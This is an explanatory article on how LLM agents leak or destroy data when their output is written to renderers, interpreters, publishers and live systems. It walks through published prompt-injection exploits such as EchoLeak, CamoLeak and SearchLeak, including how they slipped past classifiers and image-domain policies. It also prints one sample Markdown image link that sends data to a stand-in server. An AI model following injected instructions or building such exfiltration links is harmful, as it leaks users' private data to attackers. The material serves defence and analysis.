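# Data leaks and damage from LLM applications that write to systems

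## What can go wrong when a language model's output is written into a system?

A large language model (LLM) is a program that takes in text and produces text. An LLM application is any program that sends text to such a model and uses its reply. In a chatbot or translator, the reply appears on a screen and a person decides what to do about it. Many newer applications act on the reply directly by editing documentation, writing and running tests, commenting on code, sending mail and changing database records.

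An agent is an LLM application in which the model also chooses the actions. The developer supplies tools, which are functions the surrounding program can run, such as reading a file or posting a comment. The program sends the model a task and a list of these tools. The model replies with text that names a tool and its arguments. The program then runs the tool and sends back the result as text, and the loop repeats until the model produces a final answer. Because the model only produces text, all its effects on files, networks and other systems come from software that acts on that text.

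### Where text takes effect

A sink is a place where model output takes effect, and the same string can have different effects in different sinks. For example, a chat window only displays a command that deletes a folder, but a shell, the program that executes typed commands, runs it and deletes the folder. There are roughly four kinds of sink.

A renderer, such as a browser, chat window or mail program, turns text into something for a person to look at. A browser also runs the scripts in a page and fetches the images it links to. If a model's reply contains an image link with private data in its address, opening the reply can send that data to whoever runs the image's server.

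Interpreters, such as shells, test runners and database engines, run text as code. *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, an entry in the security nonprofit OWASP's list of risks, gives the example of an application that lets people query a database in ordinary language. The model translates each request into SQL, the language that databases accept. If a user asks to delete every table and nothing checks the query the model writes, the database deletes them.

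A publisher shows a model's output to people who could not see the model's input. Code-hosting sites are the most common example. A repository stores a project's code, documentation and the history of every change, and it can be public or private. Users report bugs by opening issues on the repository. A pull request is a proposed change that others can review before someone merges it into the main version. If an agent copies three lines from a private repository into its reply to a public issue, anyone can read those lines.

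A live system holds data or provides a service that people depend on, such as a customer database or a cloud account. Software teams usually keep a production system, which customers use, and a staging system, which is a copy for testing. An agent might empty a database table to get a clean test run. This is useful in staging, but in production it deletes data that people depend on, and the two commands may differ only in the address of the database.

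A single output often passes through several sinks. A test file that a model writes can appear in a public pull request, then run on a test machine and change a database.

The harm takes two forms. One is a loss of confidentiality, in which private data reaches someone who should not have it (exfiltration). The other is a loss of data or service, in which records disappear or become wrong, or a system stops working. A good backup can undo a deletion, but nothing can make a published document private again. If the leaked item is a secret (a password, key or token that grants access to a system), its owner can limit the damage by cancelling and replacing it, provided they notice before someone uses it, but a customer's medical history cannot be replaced.

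### Why a model follows text it should only read

Data leaks and damage can both result from a mistake or an attack. Attackers most often use prompt injection, which means placing text in material the model reads, such as a web page or a post in an issue tracker, so that the model follows it as an instruction. For example, a user might ask an assistant to summarise a web page that contains a sentence telling the reader to send their private files to a certain address. If the assistant has a mail tool, it may send the user's files there. This can happen without the user typing anything unusual or the attacker having an account on the user's system.

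The programmer Simon Willison named prompt injection after SQL injection, an older attack on databases, as he explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (2025). If a website builds a database command by pasting in whatever a visitor typed, a visitor can type a fragment of SQL and the database will execute it. Engineers reliably prevent this with parameterised queries, which send the command and the visitor's text to the database separately, so the database never treats the text as part of the command.

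LLMs have no reliable way to separate instructions from data. The application joins the developer's standing instructions, the user's request, the web page and the results of earlier tool calls into one sequence of tokens, the word fragments that a model processes, and the model computes its reply from all of them. A developer can put markers around the untrusted part, but the markers are tokens in the same sequence. Training can make a model less likely to follow instructions between the markers, but it doesn't eliminate the risk. According to Respan (2026), a company that sells tools for testing agents, OWASP states in the prompt injection entry of its latest list, published in August 2026, that nothing cleanly equivalent to a parameterised query exists.

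A deeper difficulty is that people want models to follow instructions they find in documents. A developer who tells an agent to set up a project according to its installation guide is asking it to follow instructions that somebody else wrote. Whether a sentence is a legitimate instruction depends on what the user intended, which the sentence itself may not show. *The Framing Gap* (Rahman and Kim, 2026) reports an experiment on gpt-4o, an OpenAI model from 2024, that fits this account. Removing the rule to keep a value confidential barely changed how often injected text extracted it, and Rahman and Kim concluded that the model had treated the text as part of its task.

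Prompt injection is easy to confuse with jailbreaking, in which a user persuades a model to break its maker's rules. Willison distinguishes them because developers who confuse the two tend to ignore both. A jailbroken chatbot mostly embarrasses its vendor, while a successful injection can cause the user to lose their data. He also distrusts products that promise to catch 95% of attacks, a rate he calls a failing grade in web security. An attacker who can reword an attack and try again has a good chance of getting past such a filter.

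### What theft requires and what breakage requires

An attacker can use prompt injection to steal private data only if the agent has access to that data, reads untrusted content, and can communicate with the outside. Willison calls this combination the "lethal trifecta". The attacker uses the untrusted content to get instructions to the model and the outside communication to get the data out.

The conditions are easy to meet by accident. An email tool that can read and send messages meets all three, because the mailbox contains private messages and anyone can write to it. Willison's other example is GitHub's official connector for agents, which could read private repositories, read public issues that anyone might have written, and open pull requests. Data can also leave through any web request, including one that loads an image, or through a link that the user only has to click. Vendors who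 fixed such flaws usually blocked only the route that a researcher had shown them, which does not protect users who combine tools from several suppliers themselves.

Accidental damage requires none of the three conditions, only write access and one wrong line of text. For example, an agent might maintain a shop's product catalogue. Everything in the catalogue is already public, the agent reads only files that the shop's staff wrote, and its machine has no outside connection, so nobody can use it to steal anything. But the agent has permission to delete entries. If it issues a delete command without the condition that limits it to discontinued products, it empties the catalogue. Agents have deleted production databases in much this way, with no attacker involved.

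An agent that holds private data and writes to a public place can leak that data by mistake, even if everything it reads comes from colleagues. An attacker who wants to cause damage needs only an agent that reads untrusted content and has write permission, because the attack doesn't require sending data out. Cutting an agent off from the internet therefore does a lot to prevent data theft but very little to prevent deletion.

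### Two categories from OWASP

OWASP, the nonprofit whose SQL scenario appears above, publishes free guidance on application security, including a list of the ten most serious risks for LLM applications. The current edition is dated August 3, 2026 (OWASP, 2026). Most of the problems in this section fall under two of its categories.

The 2025 edition of OWASP's LLM Top 10 defines improper output handling as "insufficient validation, sanitization, and handling" of model output before it passes to other components. The fault occurs between the model and the component that receives its output, as when an application puts a model's reply into a web page without neutralising the scripts in it, or passes the reply straight to a shell. MITRE's *CWE-1426*, an entry in a public catalogue of software weaknesses, advises analysts to use the code injection category, which is much older than LLMs, when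 output goes directly into a component that executes code. Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026) reports that the 2026 edition expanded improper output handling to include terminals that obey control codes hidden in text, and programs that automatically fetch whatever the output links to.

OWASP's *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency* defines excessive agency as the vulnerability that allows damaging actions in response to "unexpected, ambiguous or manipulated outputs", whatever caused the model to go wrong. The triggers it lists include prompt injection and invented answers to innocent but badly written prompts. Respan's summary of the 2026 edition gives the same definition and the same three root causes. The first is excessive functionality, as when a developer wants an agent to read documents but installs a tool that can also modify and delete them. The second is excessive permissions, as when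 a tool meant for reading connects to a database with an account that can also update and delete. The third is excessive autonomy, where the application carries out a high-impact action that nobody has confirmed.

Some cases fall under only one of the categories. A chatbot with no tools can still return a script that runs in a visitor's browser, which is improper output handling but involves no agency. The catalogue agent's delete command was valid SQL, so escaping and syntax checks would not have stopped it. The problem was that the agent could delete the whole catalogue without being asked. Many incidents fall under both categories. OWASP lists its scenario of the deleted tables under output handling, but either a check on the query or a read-only database account would have prevented the loss.

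Excessive agency rose from sixth place in the 2025 edition of OWASP's ranking to third in 2026, while improper output handling fell from fifth to tenth. The 2026 edition was the first to weigh real incidents alongside practitioners' votes, and in OWASP (2026)'s announcement, Michael Bargury of the security firm Zenity names excessive agency as the risk on which the two agree most clearly. Invicti attributes the fall of output handling to the growing urgency of the other entries. Because the ranking is relative, the fall is weak evidence that the risk itself has shrunk.

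### A bot that updates documentation

Suppose a company that sells a software library keeps its code and documentation in a public repository, and its next release and some internal notes in a private one. Anyone can open an issue. When an issue reports an error in the documentation, an LLM bot reads it, searches both repositories for the right answer, rewrites the page, runs the page's code samples to check them, opens a pull request and replies to the person who reported the error.

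After a maintainer merges the change, the company's build pipeline rebuilds the documentation website and puts it online. A build pipeline, also called CI/CD, is the set of automatic jobs that test, package and release code after a change. Rebuilding and publishing the site requires secrets, including a token for uploading the site and a key to the staging database that the code samples use. The bot runs as a job in the same pipeline, so it can access those secrets unless someone has restricted it.

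| What the bot does | Input or sink | Where a leak could occur | Where a breakage could occur |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reads the issue | Untrusted input | An injection can enter here | An injection can enter here |
| Searches both repositories | Private input | Private text is now in front of the model | None, if the access is read-only |
| Runs the code samples | Interpreter, and perhaps a live system | A sample prints a secret to a public log or sends it over the network | A sample deletes files or alters a database |
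| Opens a pull request | Publisher | Private text becomes public at once | None until a job runs the change or someone merges it |
| Replies to the issue | Publisher | Private text becomes public at once | Little beyond a misleading answer |
| Updates the website, after the merge | Live system, and a renderer for each reader | A page contains private text, or makes readers' browsers contact an outside server | A faulty page or setting takes the site down |

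All three of Willison's conditions hold, so a stranger could write an issue that makes the bot copy private notes into its reply. The bot can also leak these notes when the person writing the issue means no harm. For example, a customer might ask why a setting doesn't work, and the bot might quote the explanation from an internal note about the next release.

As an example of breakage, suppose one code sample begins by resetting the database, which is reasonable in staging. Someone has since given the pipeline a production key for an unrelated job, and the sample uses that key. The reset deletes customer records, even though the bot did its task as described. In OWASP's terms, the key had excessive permissions, and running the sample without approval was excessive autonomy.

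In this design, a person reviews the pull request before the change becomes part of the documentation, which protects the website from a bad edit. But by then the code samples have already run and the reply has been posted. In a public repository, the pull request is visible as soon as it opens, so anyone could copy a secret in it before the reviewer spots it.

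## How can a document or reply written by a model send data out when it is opened?

An agent with no mail tool or web access can still send private data to a stranger by writing an image link with the data in its address. Researchers have found this leak in assistants from Microsoft, OpenAI, Anthropic and Google since 2023.

### From hidden text to a server log

Chat windows, wikis and code-hosting sites usually display text written in Markdown, a notation that uses punctuation for formatting, such as asterisks around a word for italics. An exclamation mark followed by a caption in square brackets and an address in parentheses inserts an image, which the reader's program has to fetch from that address.

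The security firm PromptArmor's *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data* documents each step of the leak in HuggingChat, an app for chatting with a range of models:

1. A user uploaded a file with a company's quarterly revenue and costs, added a web page of customer reviews, and asked how to win back one dissatisfied reviewer.
2. The page contained text that a person could not see but that the model received along with the reviews. It presented a picture of the quarterly figures as part of the answer, and gave the address of a server that the testers controlled.
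3. The model wrote an image link with the figures in its address.
4. The user's browser asked the server for the picture.
5. The server recorded the address in its log, where the testers read the figures.

With an invented address, a link of this kind looks like this:

`![chart](https://pictures.example/dot.png?d=Q3_revenue_was_4.2_million_euros)`

The part of the web address up to the equals sign directs the request to the attacker's server, and the rest is the stolen data. In PromptArmor's test, the server returned a picture one pixel wide, so nothing looked wrong on the screen. The picture doesn't have to exist, because the server has already received the data by the time it returns a "not found" error.

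Because the reader's own browser makes the request, taking away the agent's network tools does nothing to stop this leak.

The address above has 35 characters of routing and 32 of data, but it could be much longer. The HTTP standard, which defines how browsers and servers communicate, recommends that software support addresses of at least 8,000 characters. With the same routing, that would leave 7,965 characters for data, or about 1,300 English words before encoding. Encoding is needed because addresses cannot contain spaces and several other characters. Base64, a common encoding, turns every three characters into four, which reduces the capacity to just under 6,000 characters. Embrace the Red's *Bing Chat*, a demonstration from 2023, used injected text to request a 200-character summary of the page and the conversation, which comes to 268 characters in base64. A reply can also contain several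 images, each with its own address. An attacker rarely needs that much space, because a login code has about six characters and a typical access key a few dozen.

### The same text in different programs

A plain-text editor shows the example link as a line of text and doesn't contact the server. A renderer recognises the notation and fetches the picture. Microsoft apparently fixed this leak in its Azure AI Playground in 2023 by inserting a single space between the brackets, according to Embrace the Red's *Microsoft Fixes Data Exfiltration Vulnerability in Azure AI Playground*. The page then no longer treated the text as an image, although the private data was still in it.

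An ordinary link can carry the same data in its address, but the browser sends it only when the reader clicks the link. Images need no click because the browser fetches them automatically to display the page. The security firm Checkmarx calls the image case zero-click exfiltration and the link case one-click exfiltration.

According to Embrace the Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*, Anthropic fixed a data exfiltration vulnerability in its assistant Claude in July 2023 by no longer loading images automatically and making the user click "Show Image" first. This helps, but it is a fairly weak barrier because a user who has asked for a chart has good reason to click.

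Plain text is safe only if every program that later handles it treats it as plain text. Someone may paste a command-line tool's output into a ticket, and the ticketing system may render it. Many chat and ticketing systems also fetch a link's destination to show a preview, so the link can send data out without a click. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data*, a guide for people who monitor networks, therefore advises checking every program that handles the output, including terminals and code editors.

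### Documents that stay

A README (the front page of a code repository), a wiki page or a ticket may have hundreds of readers and stay in place for years, while a chat reply usually has one reader. If an agent has written private data into an image address on such a page, the data is sent to the server at that address each time someone opens the page. Each request also reveals the time of the visit and often the reader's network address.

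For the documentation bot, the first person to open the page may well be the maintainer who reviews the pull request. If the review page renders images, opening it triggers the leak. In a public repository the leak adds little, since the pull request is already public. The image matters more on an internal wiki or a private ticket, because it sends out data from a page that the attacker has no permission to open.

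Messages that an agent sends to its own user can also leak data when opened. Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent that works with a user's files, could send messages to that user's inbox without approval. Willison noted in May 2026, in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, that these messages could contain external images, so opening one could send data to an attacker. Microsoft's file storage can also create download links that need no login. An attacker could put one of these links in an image address and get a whole file through a request of ordinary length.

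An attack can also start from a stored document. In *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend*, veganmosfet built a chatbot with Dify, a platform for making LLM applications, and gave it two PDF files to answer questions from. One file contained hidden instructions about a particular topic. Whenever a user asked about that topic, the application retrieved the file, the model followed the instructions, and the user's name was sent out in an image address. One such file in a shared collection can therefore affect every later user who asks about that topic.

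Images can leak data without an attacker. Some public services, such as QuickChart and Mermaid.ink, which trackr.live gives as examples, draw charts and diagrams from data in the image address. If an agent illustrates an internal wiki page this way, the data goes to an outside company each time someone loads the image. The service is working as intended, but whoever asked for the page may not have meant to share the data.

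### The first reports and fixes

Johann Rehberger and Roman Samoilenko independently found the leak in ChatGPT in spring 2023, SecurityWeek reported. *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* (Willison, 2023) describes Samoilenko's version, in which a web page added instructions to any text a visitor copied, and the visitor pasted them into ChatGPT without noticing. Rehberger, who publishes his findings on the blog Embrace the Red, then tested a series of other assistants.

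Bing Chat could read the web page a user was viewing, so an attacker could use a comment or an advertisement on the page to steal other data from it. Rehberger reported this to Microsoft on April 8, 2023, and learned on June 15 that a fix was in place. As far as he could tell, the fix relied at least partly on a content security policy, a list of the domains from which a browser may load a page's contents. After the fix, Bing Chat could show images from only a few Microsoft domains.

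OpenAI heard of the ChatGPT leak in the same month but did not act until December 2023. Embrace the Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* reports that the ChatGPT website then began checking with an OpenAI server whether an image's address was safe before loading it. Rehberger set up a separate address for each of 36 letters and digits and found that nine of the addresses still loaded. He could send out the word "hi" by requesting one image per letter. The iPhone app did not have the check at that point.

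GitHub's Copilot Chat, a programming assistant, had the same flaw in its extension for the code editor VS Code. Instructions in a source file could make the assistant send out earlier parts of the conversation. Rehberger reported this in February 2024, and GitHub confirmed a fix that June. Outsiders could not easily tell what had changed. Embrace the Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat* concludes that the extension apparently stopped rendering Markdown images altogether, while Willison's note, also titled *GitHub Copilot Chat*, describes a block on images from untrusted domains.

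Each of these fixes changed only how one program displays text. The model was still as likely to write the link, so each app and website needed its own fix. HuggingChat still rendered images from any domain when PromptArmor reported the problem in December 2025. PromptArmor published its findings after getting no reply.

### Three leaks through trusted services

By 2025, Microsoft and GitHub had both limited the domains from which their assistants could load images. Three published exploits got around the limit by using a service on a trusted domain to pass a request on to someone else.

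**EchoLeak.** Microsoft 365 Copilot answers an employee's questions using that person's mail, files and chat history. In January 2025 the research group Aim Labs reported to Microsoft that an outsider could steal data from these sources by sending the employee an email. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) gives the discoverers' account of the defences they had to get past.

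Microsoft ran a classifier to catch injected instructions, but the email got past it because its instructions were addressed to the human recipient and never mentioned an AI. Copilot also removed outside links and images from its answers, but only those written in the most common Markdown notation. It did not remove those written in another notation, which puts the address on a separate line. Finally, a content security policy blocked images from unknown domains, but it allowed Microsoft Teams, which had a service that fetches a web address on request. The browser contacted Teams, and Teams then contacted the attacker's server with the data in the address.

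"Zero-click" here means that the employee did not have to open the email or click on anything, though the attack still required them to ask Copilot a question that led it to retrieve the email. To make retrieval likely, Aim Labs wrote a long email with sections on many common workplace subjects.

Microsoft fixed the flaw on its own servers in May 2025, before Aim Labs published it on June 11, and customers didn't have to install anything. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reports that Microsoft found no sign that anyone had exploited it. The paper also describes a change that makes Copilot strip images and the less common link notation from content that comes in from outside. The change removes the route that Aim Labs used but doesn't stop the model from following instructions in an email.

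EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711) was new mainly because the user did not have to point the assistant at the attacker's material. Reddy and Gujral call it the first known use of prompt injection to steal data from a production AI system, which seems too strong because Rehberger had extracted data from Bing Chat two years earlier. Willison (2025), commenting on *Breaking down 'EchoLeak'*, called EchoLeak an extended variant of an attack already seen in a dozen products.

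Legit Security's *CamoLeak* describes a flaw that the company's researcher found in June 2025 in Copilot Chat on GitHub's website. GitHub lets people put comments in a pull request description that don't appear on the page. Copilot could read them, and it worked with the permissions of whoever asked it a question. A stranger could therefore leave a hidden comment in a public pull request and wait for someone with access to private repositories to ask Copilot to explain the change.

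GitHub's content security policy blocked images from outside domains. To show outside images in README files, GitHub uses Camo, a proxy server that fetches them for the reader. Camo accepts only addresses that GitHub has signed in advance, so the model could not write a new address with data in it. The researcher got around this by having GitHub sign one address for each letter and symbol beforehand. The hidden comment supplied the whole set, and Copilot spelled out the private text as a row of invisible images. The researcher's server received the requests in order, one for each character.

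This is far slower than putting everything in one address, since 200 characters need 200 images, but it was enough to extract the description of an unpatched vulnerability from a private project. Copilot could also search a victim's code for the name of an Amazon cloud key and send out what it found. GitHub responded by turning off image rendering in Copilot Chat completely, and said it had fixed the flaw as of August 14.

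Camo offers less protection for a file that an agent writes. According to Legit Security, GitHub automatically signs the addresses of outside images in a README when someone commits the file. If an agent had already put private data in one of those addresses, GitHub would presumably sign it too, and Camo would pass the data on.

Varonis' *SearchLeak* (June 2026) described another leak from Microsoft 365 Copilot, this time from its enterprise search page. The attack began with a link to a genuine Microsoft address that included a search query containing instructions. After a single click on the link, Copilot followed those instructions as if the victim had typed them. It searched the victim's mail and wrote an image link containing a message title, which might include a login code.

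Microsoft tried to stop images in Copilot's answers from loading by marking each finished answer as code, so that the browser would show the image's markup as text. But the page displayed the answer while Copilot was still writing it, so the browser requested the image before the answer was marked. A content security policy also limited where images could come from, but it allowed Bing, whose image search fetches a picture from any address a user supplies. Bing's request for the image therefore carried the data to the attacker's server.

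Microsoft's notice for CVE-2026-42824, *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), rates the flaw critical, lists it as not exploited, and states that Microsoft has fully mitigated it and that customers don't need to act. The notice doesn't explain what Microsoft changed, so outsiders can't tell from it whether the company closed the timing gap, the route through Bing, or both.

An attacker can also get data through a trusted domain that doesn't forward anything. Willison's list includes ForcedLeak, a 2025 exploit of Salesforce's customer-service agent, Agentforce. Salesforce's policy still allowed images from a domain whose registration had expired, so the researchers registered it. In the mail program Superhuman, the policy allowed a Google domain that hosts online forms. Loading an image address on that domain could submit a form, so the attacker could collect a user's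 emails as form responses.

### How newer models respond to the published attacks

All these leaks require the model to follow the injected text, which newer models do less often. In *Replication of Agentic Security Events*, Wang, Alam and colleagues (2026) rebuilt twelve published injection exploits on shipped products, including EchoLeak and ForcedLeak, as offline simulations. They ran five recent models from OpenAI, Anthropic, Google and DeepSeek three times on each exploit. The models caused harm in 2 of the 180 sessions.

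This number makes the models look safer than they are. The injected text reached the model in only 108 of the 166 sessions with usable logs, so the other 58 did not test whether the model would resist it. In four of the original exploits, data leaked when the product's interface rendered an image. The first versions of the simulations did not reproduce this step, so a model could have written exactly the link the attacker wanted without any data getting out.

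Wang and colleagues then restored details missing from the simulations, such as image rendering, and reran eight of the exploits. A model counted as reproducing an exploit if it caused the harm at least once. GPT-4.1-mini, an OpenAI model from 2025, reproduced five of the eight, and each of the five newer models reproduced between none and four. For the exploits it reproduced, GPT-4.1-mini caused harm in five to ten of ten sessions, compared with none of 100 sessions without the attack. CamoLeak, ForcedLeak and a leak from the note-taking program Notion all worked in the corrected simulations, and the recent model DeepSeek-V4-Flash also reproduced the Notion leak.

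The results are good evidence that the choice of model matters, and that most of these attacks would now fail against at least some recent models. But a product may still run an older model, often without its users knowing. The number of runs was also small. Wang and colleagues calculate that an exploit that fails in all 15 sessions could still have a true success rate of up to about 20%.

EchoLeak did not work on any model tested in the simulation. Claude Haiku 4.5 labelled the injected requests as attacks and refused them, so it could recognise this version of the attack. The result does not show whether Microsoft's fixes work, because the simulation did not include Microsoft's filters or its Teams service.

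New attacks have continued to work on live products. In July 2026 Willison described one that the researcher Ayush Paul found in Claude. Anthropic allowed Claude's web tool to open only addresses that the user had typed or that had appeared in search results or fetched pages, so that the model could not write private data into a new address. Paul built a site with a separate link for each letter and a message that presented the links as a login procedure. Claude spelled out the user's name by following the links in order, and the site recorded which ones it opened. Paul obtained the user's home city and employer in the same way. Anthropic has since stopped the tool from following links that it finds on fetched pages.

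## How do coding agents publish private material by mistake?

Nearly all the leaks in the previous section needed an attacker to plant instructions and collect the data. A coding agent, which edits and runs code for a developer, can also leak data when no one intends harm, by completing its task and putting the result where outsiders can read it. Of the 72 incidents with real-world harm that Wang and colleagues studied, 62 involved no attacker, though these include deletions as well as leaks.

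### Screenshots for a reviewer

When a developer changes how a program looks, reviewers want to see it before and after the change. In a browser, the developer can drag a screenshot into a GitHub pull request, and only people with access to the repository can open it. Coding agents usually work by typing commands. Until September 2026, GitHub's command-line tool could send only text, so an agent could take a screenshot but had no official way to attach it.

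*PixelLeak*, published by the security company Glow on September 29, 2026, reports that many coding agents uploaded screenshots to public repositories, where anyone could see them, not only the reviewers of the private code. Glow found more than 13,000 internal images in over 900 repositories, from developers at over 300 organisations. Corvin (2026), in *AI agents leak 13K screenshots from 343 tech firms*, puts the exact number of organisations at 343.

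In 93% of cases, the repository was under an employee's own username, where a security team that checks only the company's GitHub account will miss it. At a manufacturer with over 100,000 employees, a developer asked an agent to verify a fix to an internal billing screen. The agent created a public repository in the developer's personal account and posted screenshots of a utility company's billing records. The screenshots were still online when Glow contacted the manufacturer.

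About a third of the affected organisations had developers running gitshot, a free tool that uploads images for code reviews. On first use, it creates a public repository in the user's account. The tool's README, by the developer vipulgupta2048, warns against uploading "internal dashboards" this way. But gitshot also comes as a skill, a set of saved instructions that an agent loads when a task needs them, so a developer who asks for a screenshot may never see the warning. One financial firm exposed its treasury console and a withdrawal screen for a named client. People can run gitshot too, so its traces alone don't prove that an agent chose it, but Glow reports that at several large organisations the agent found the tool on its own.

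Agents at one software vendor began publishing screenshots as a workaround in early July, and within a week more than a dozen of them had saved the method as a skill to use on every development ticket. They uploaded over a thousand screenshots and recordings, with descriptions of features that were weeks or months from release.

Glow reproduced the leak with Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, running the model Opus 5 on a private version of the game Minesweeper. The agent explained that reviewers had to see the images, that GitHub could not show them from a private repository, and that the project's repository was to contain only its one web page, "so I created a new public repo". It mentioned that the project was private, but only as a technical obstacle. Glow calls this reasoning representative of many affected organisations. The test shows that a recent model can make this mistake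 without an attacker, but not how often. The rate can't be worked out from the count of 13,000 images either, because nobody knows how many screenshots agents handled safely.

The agent had alternatives to a public repository. The README of *gh-image* (2026), an add-on available by June, describes a way to attach images from the command line that keeps images in private repositories private. The add-on copies the browser's upload method, which requires cookies from a logged-in browser, according to gitshot's README. It therefore presumably needs the developer's browser login, which is a lot of access to give an agent just to attach a picture. The agent could also have asked the developer to attach the images.

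On September 1, GitHub (2026) added an `--attach` option to its command-line tool, which uploads an image or video with an issue, pull request or comment. Glow began notifying organisations on September 9, so the change was not a response to those notices. The option removes the main reason for the workaround, but only for agents that use the new version. It doesn't yet support GitHub Enterprise Server, the edition that companies run themselves, and an agent with a saved skill may keep using a public repository.

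To find existing leaks, Glow recommends starting with everyone who has committed code to a private repository, including former employees, and checking their personal accounts. The search should cover files attached to releases, which don't appear in a repository's file listing. To prevent leaks, Glow advises that security teams, rather than individual developers, should control whether agents can work unattended (quoted in Markovic, 2026, *AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos*).

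### Secrets written into code

Programs need secrets to connect to databases and paid services. A careful programmer stores the secret outside the code, and the program looks it up when it runs. Suppose the documentation bot writes a code sample that connects to the staging database. It could write either of these lines:

```
connect("staging.example", key="EXAMPLE-KEY-123")
connect("staging.example", key=os.environ["STAGING_KEY"])
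```

Both lines work when the bot tests them, but publishing the first reveals the key, while publishing the second reveals only the name of a setting. *AI Coding Tools and Public Repository Data Leaks*, by CybelAngel, a company that searches the internet for its clients' data, argues that models are geared toward code that works, and that people new to programming often don't know to ask for secure code too.

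Setup guides can also contribute to leaks. GitGuardian's *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026* (2026) describes popular guides that put keys directly into the configuration files for MCP (Model Context Protocol), a standard for connecting models to tools. GitGuardian, which sells software for detecting secrets, found 24,008 different secrets in such files on public GitHub in 2025, and 2,117 of them worked when it checked.

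GitGuardian also found 28.65 million new secrets across 1.94 billion public commits (saved sets of changes to a repository) in 2025, 34% more secrets than the year before. It reports a leak rate of 1.5% for all commits and 3.2% for those that name Claude Code as co-author. The Claude Code commits accounted for 0.4% of all commits, or roughly 7.8 million, and 0.9% of the leaks.

GitGuardian's 1.5% is probably the number of secrets per hundred commits, because dividing 28.65 million secrets by 1.94 billion commits gives the same number. GitGuardian describes it as the share of commits that contain a secret, but a commit with three secrets would count three times.

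The 3.2% is also hard to reconcile with GitGuardian's monthly figures. These peak at 31 secrets per 1,000 Claude Code commits in August, about 2.4 times the human rate, and fall to 13 in December, about equal to the human rate. A yearly average cannot exceed the highest month. December alone had 2.16 million of the Claude Code commits, so even if every other month had matched the August peak, the yearly rate would be only about 2.6%. The yearly and monthly figures must therefore be based on different counts. "Twice the baseline" describes 2025 as a whole, but the gap had closed by the end of the year.

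*API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary* (2026) cautions that GitGuardian's figures for 2024 are a vendor's measurement, not a census. The count depends on which detectors are used and how duplicates are treated, and a detected secret may never have worked. The same limitations apply to the 2025 totals, but they matter less when comparing Claude Code commits with other commits if the same detectors scanned both.

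### The tool, the user or the project?

Commit size could explain most of the gap. GitGuardian reports that from April onward, Claude Code commits averaged about twice as many lines as human ones, which would make the leak rate per line about the same. Its account of the later trend is inconsistent, since it says both that the sizes evened out by the end of the year and that Claude Code commits remain larger.

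Other research also finds that agents tend to make bigger changes. *Detecting AI Coding Agents in Open Source* (2026) found that a sample of 41 commits by the agent OpenHands added a median of 52 lines, while 58 human commits in the same projects added a median of 28. *Agent or Human?* (2026) compared commits from the same repositories and period. It found that Claude Code changed more lines per file than people did, but found no clear difference for the coding tool Cursor.

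The type of project may matter too. GitGuardian compared Claude Code's commits with the rest of GitHub, not with other commits to the same projects. Applications built around AI services need many keys, and leaks of keys for these services rose by 81% in 2025. GitGuardian also reports that 54% of the developers active on public GitHub in 2025 made their first commit that year. If beginners and builders of AI applications used Claude Code more than other developers, its commits would contain more secrets even if the tool made no difference.

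GitGuardian warns against reading the gap as "a simple tool failure", because developers still control what they commit. This is a fair point when a developer reads the changes first, but a weaker one when an agent commits and publishes them unattended. GitGuardian's data can't separate these cases. It identifies Claude Code's commits by a line in the commit message that names the tool as co-author, which doesn't show whether anyone checked the code. GitGuardian counts commits without this line as human.

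Some evidence suggests that the tool affects the leak rate. GitGuardian links the fall in Claude Code's leak rate to the release of the model Claude Sonnet 4.5 in late September 2025. But the rate had peaked in July and August, so the fall probably began before the release. Claude Code commits also grew from 22 in January to millions by December, so the people and projects behind them must have changed.

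*Not All Agents Are Equal* (2026) found secrets written into the code in 0.9% of pull requests by agents and 2.2% of those by people. The rate was 3.3% for Claude Code but 0.5% for both Cursor and OpenAI's Codex. This is strong evidence against the idea that AI-written code in general leaks more secrets. The difference between products seems to come from Claude Code, its users or their projects, but these rates can't show which, because people choose different products for different work. A better test would give the same developers similar tasks with and without each tool.

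### A consultant's notes

An agent can also publish a whole folder at once. On March 28, 2026, CybelAngel found a public GitHub repository containing 880 notes belonging to a senior consultant at a French technology consultancy. The notes named clients, their staff and job candidates. One recorded a January meeting with a client's head of data about the company's strategy and investment priorities. CybelAngel sent formal reports to six of its own clients, and the repository was secure about 48 hours after it appeared.

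The evidence in CybelAngel's *How an AI Tool Pushed Client Strategy Notes to GitHub* does not fully support the title's claim. The repository contained a CLAUDE.md file, which Claude Code generates to describe a folder for later sessions. The file described the folder as synced through Apple's iCloud and not a git repository (git is the version-control program GitHub is built on). The repository had no list of files to exclude, and its README was a single line. The note-taking program, Obsidian, had no plugin for publishing to GitHub.

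CybelAngel infers from this that the consultant used Claude Code on the notes, which is likely. It acknowledges that it cannot confirm whether Claude Code published the folder while carrying out a request or the consultant did so by hand afterwards. The missing exclusion list and the short README suggest haste, but a person in a hurry could also have published the folder that way. The CLAUDE.md file, which CybelAngel calls a striking self-contradiction, may date from before anyone turned the folder into a repository. A log of the agent's session could show who published the folder, and might also show whether the consultant had asked for a backup on GitHub without specifying that it should be private.

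### Why deleting the file does not undo the leak

Git keeps old versions of files. If a developer commits a file containing a key on Monday and deletes it on Tuesday, the key is gone from the current version but remains in Monday's commit. Anyone who downloads the repository normally gets that commit too. The developer can rewrite the history to remove the commit, or delete the whole repository, but neither affects copies that other people have already made.

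Such copies can appear very quickly because automatic scanners watch public repositories. GitGuardian's free service, which checks public commits and emails the author as soon as it finds a secret, sent 2.5 million warnings in 2025. Attackers can watch the same commits, so CybelAngel advises people to assume that someone has seen any secret in a public commit and to replace it immediately.

Copies of a secret can still work after the file containing it is taken offline, but cancelling the secret makes every copy useless. GitGuardian scanned publicly exposed Docker registries, which are servers that store packaged programs. About 18% of them went offline within weeks of the scan, but in several cases the secrets from them still worked.

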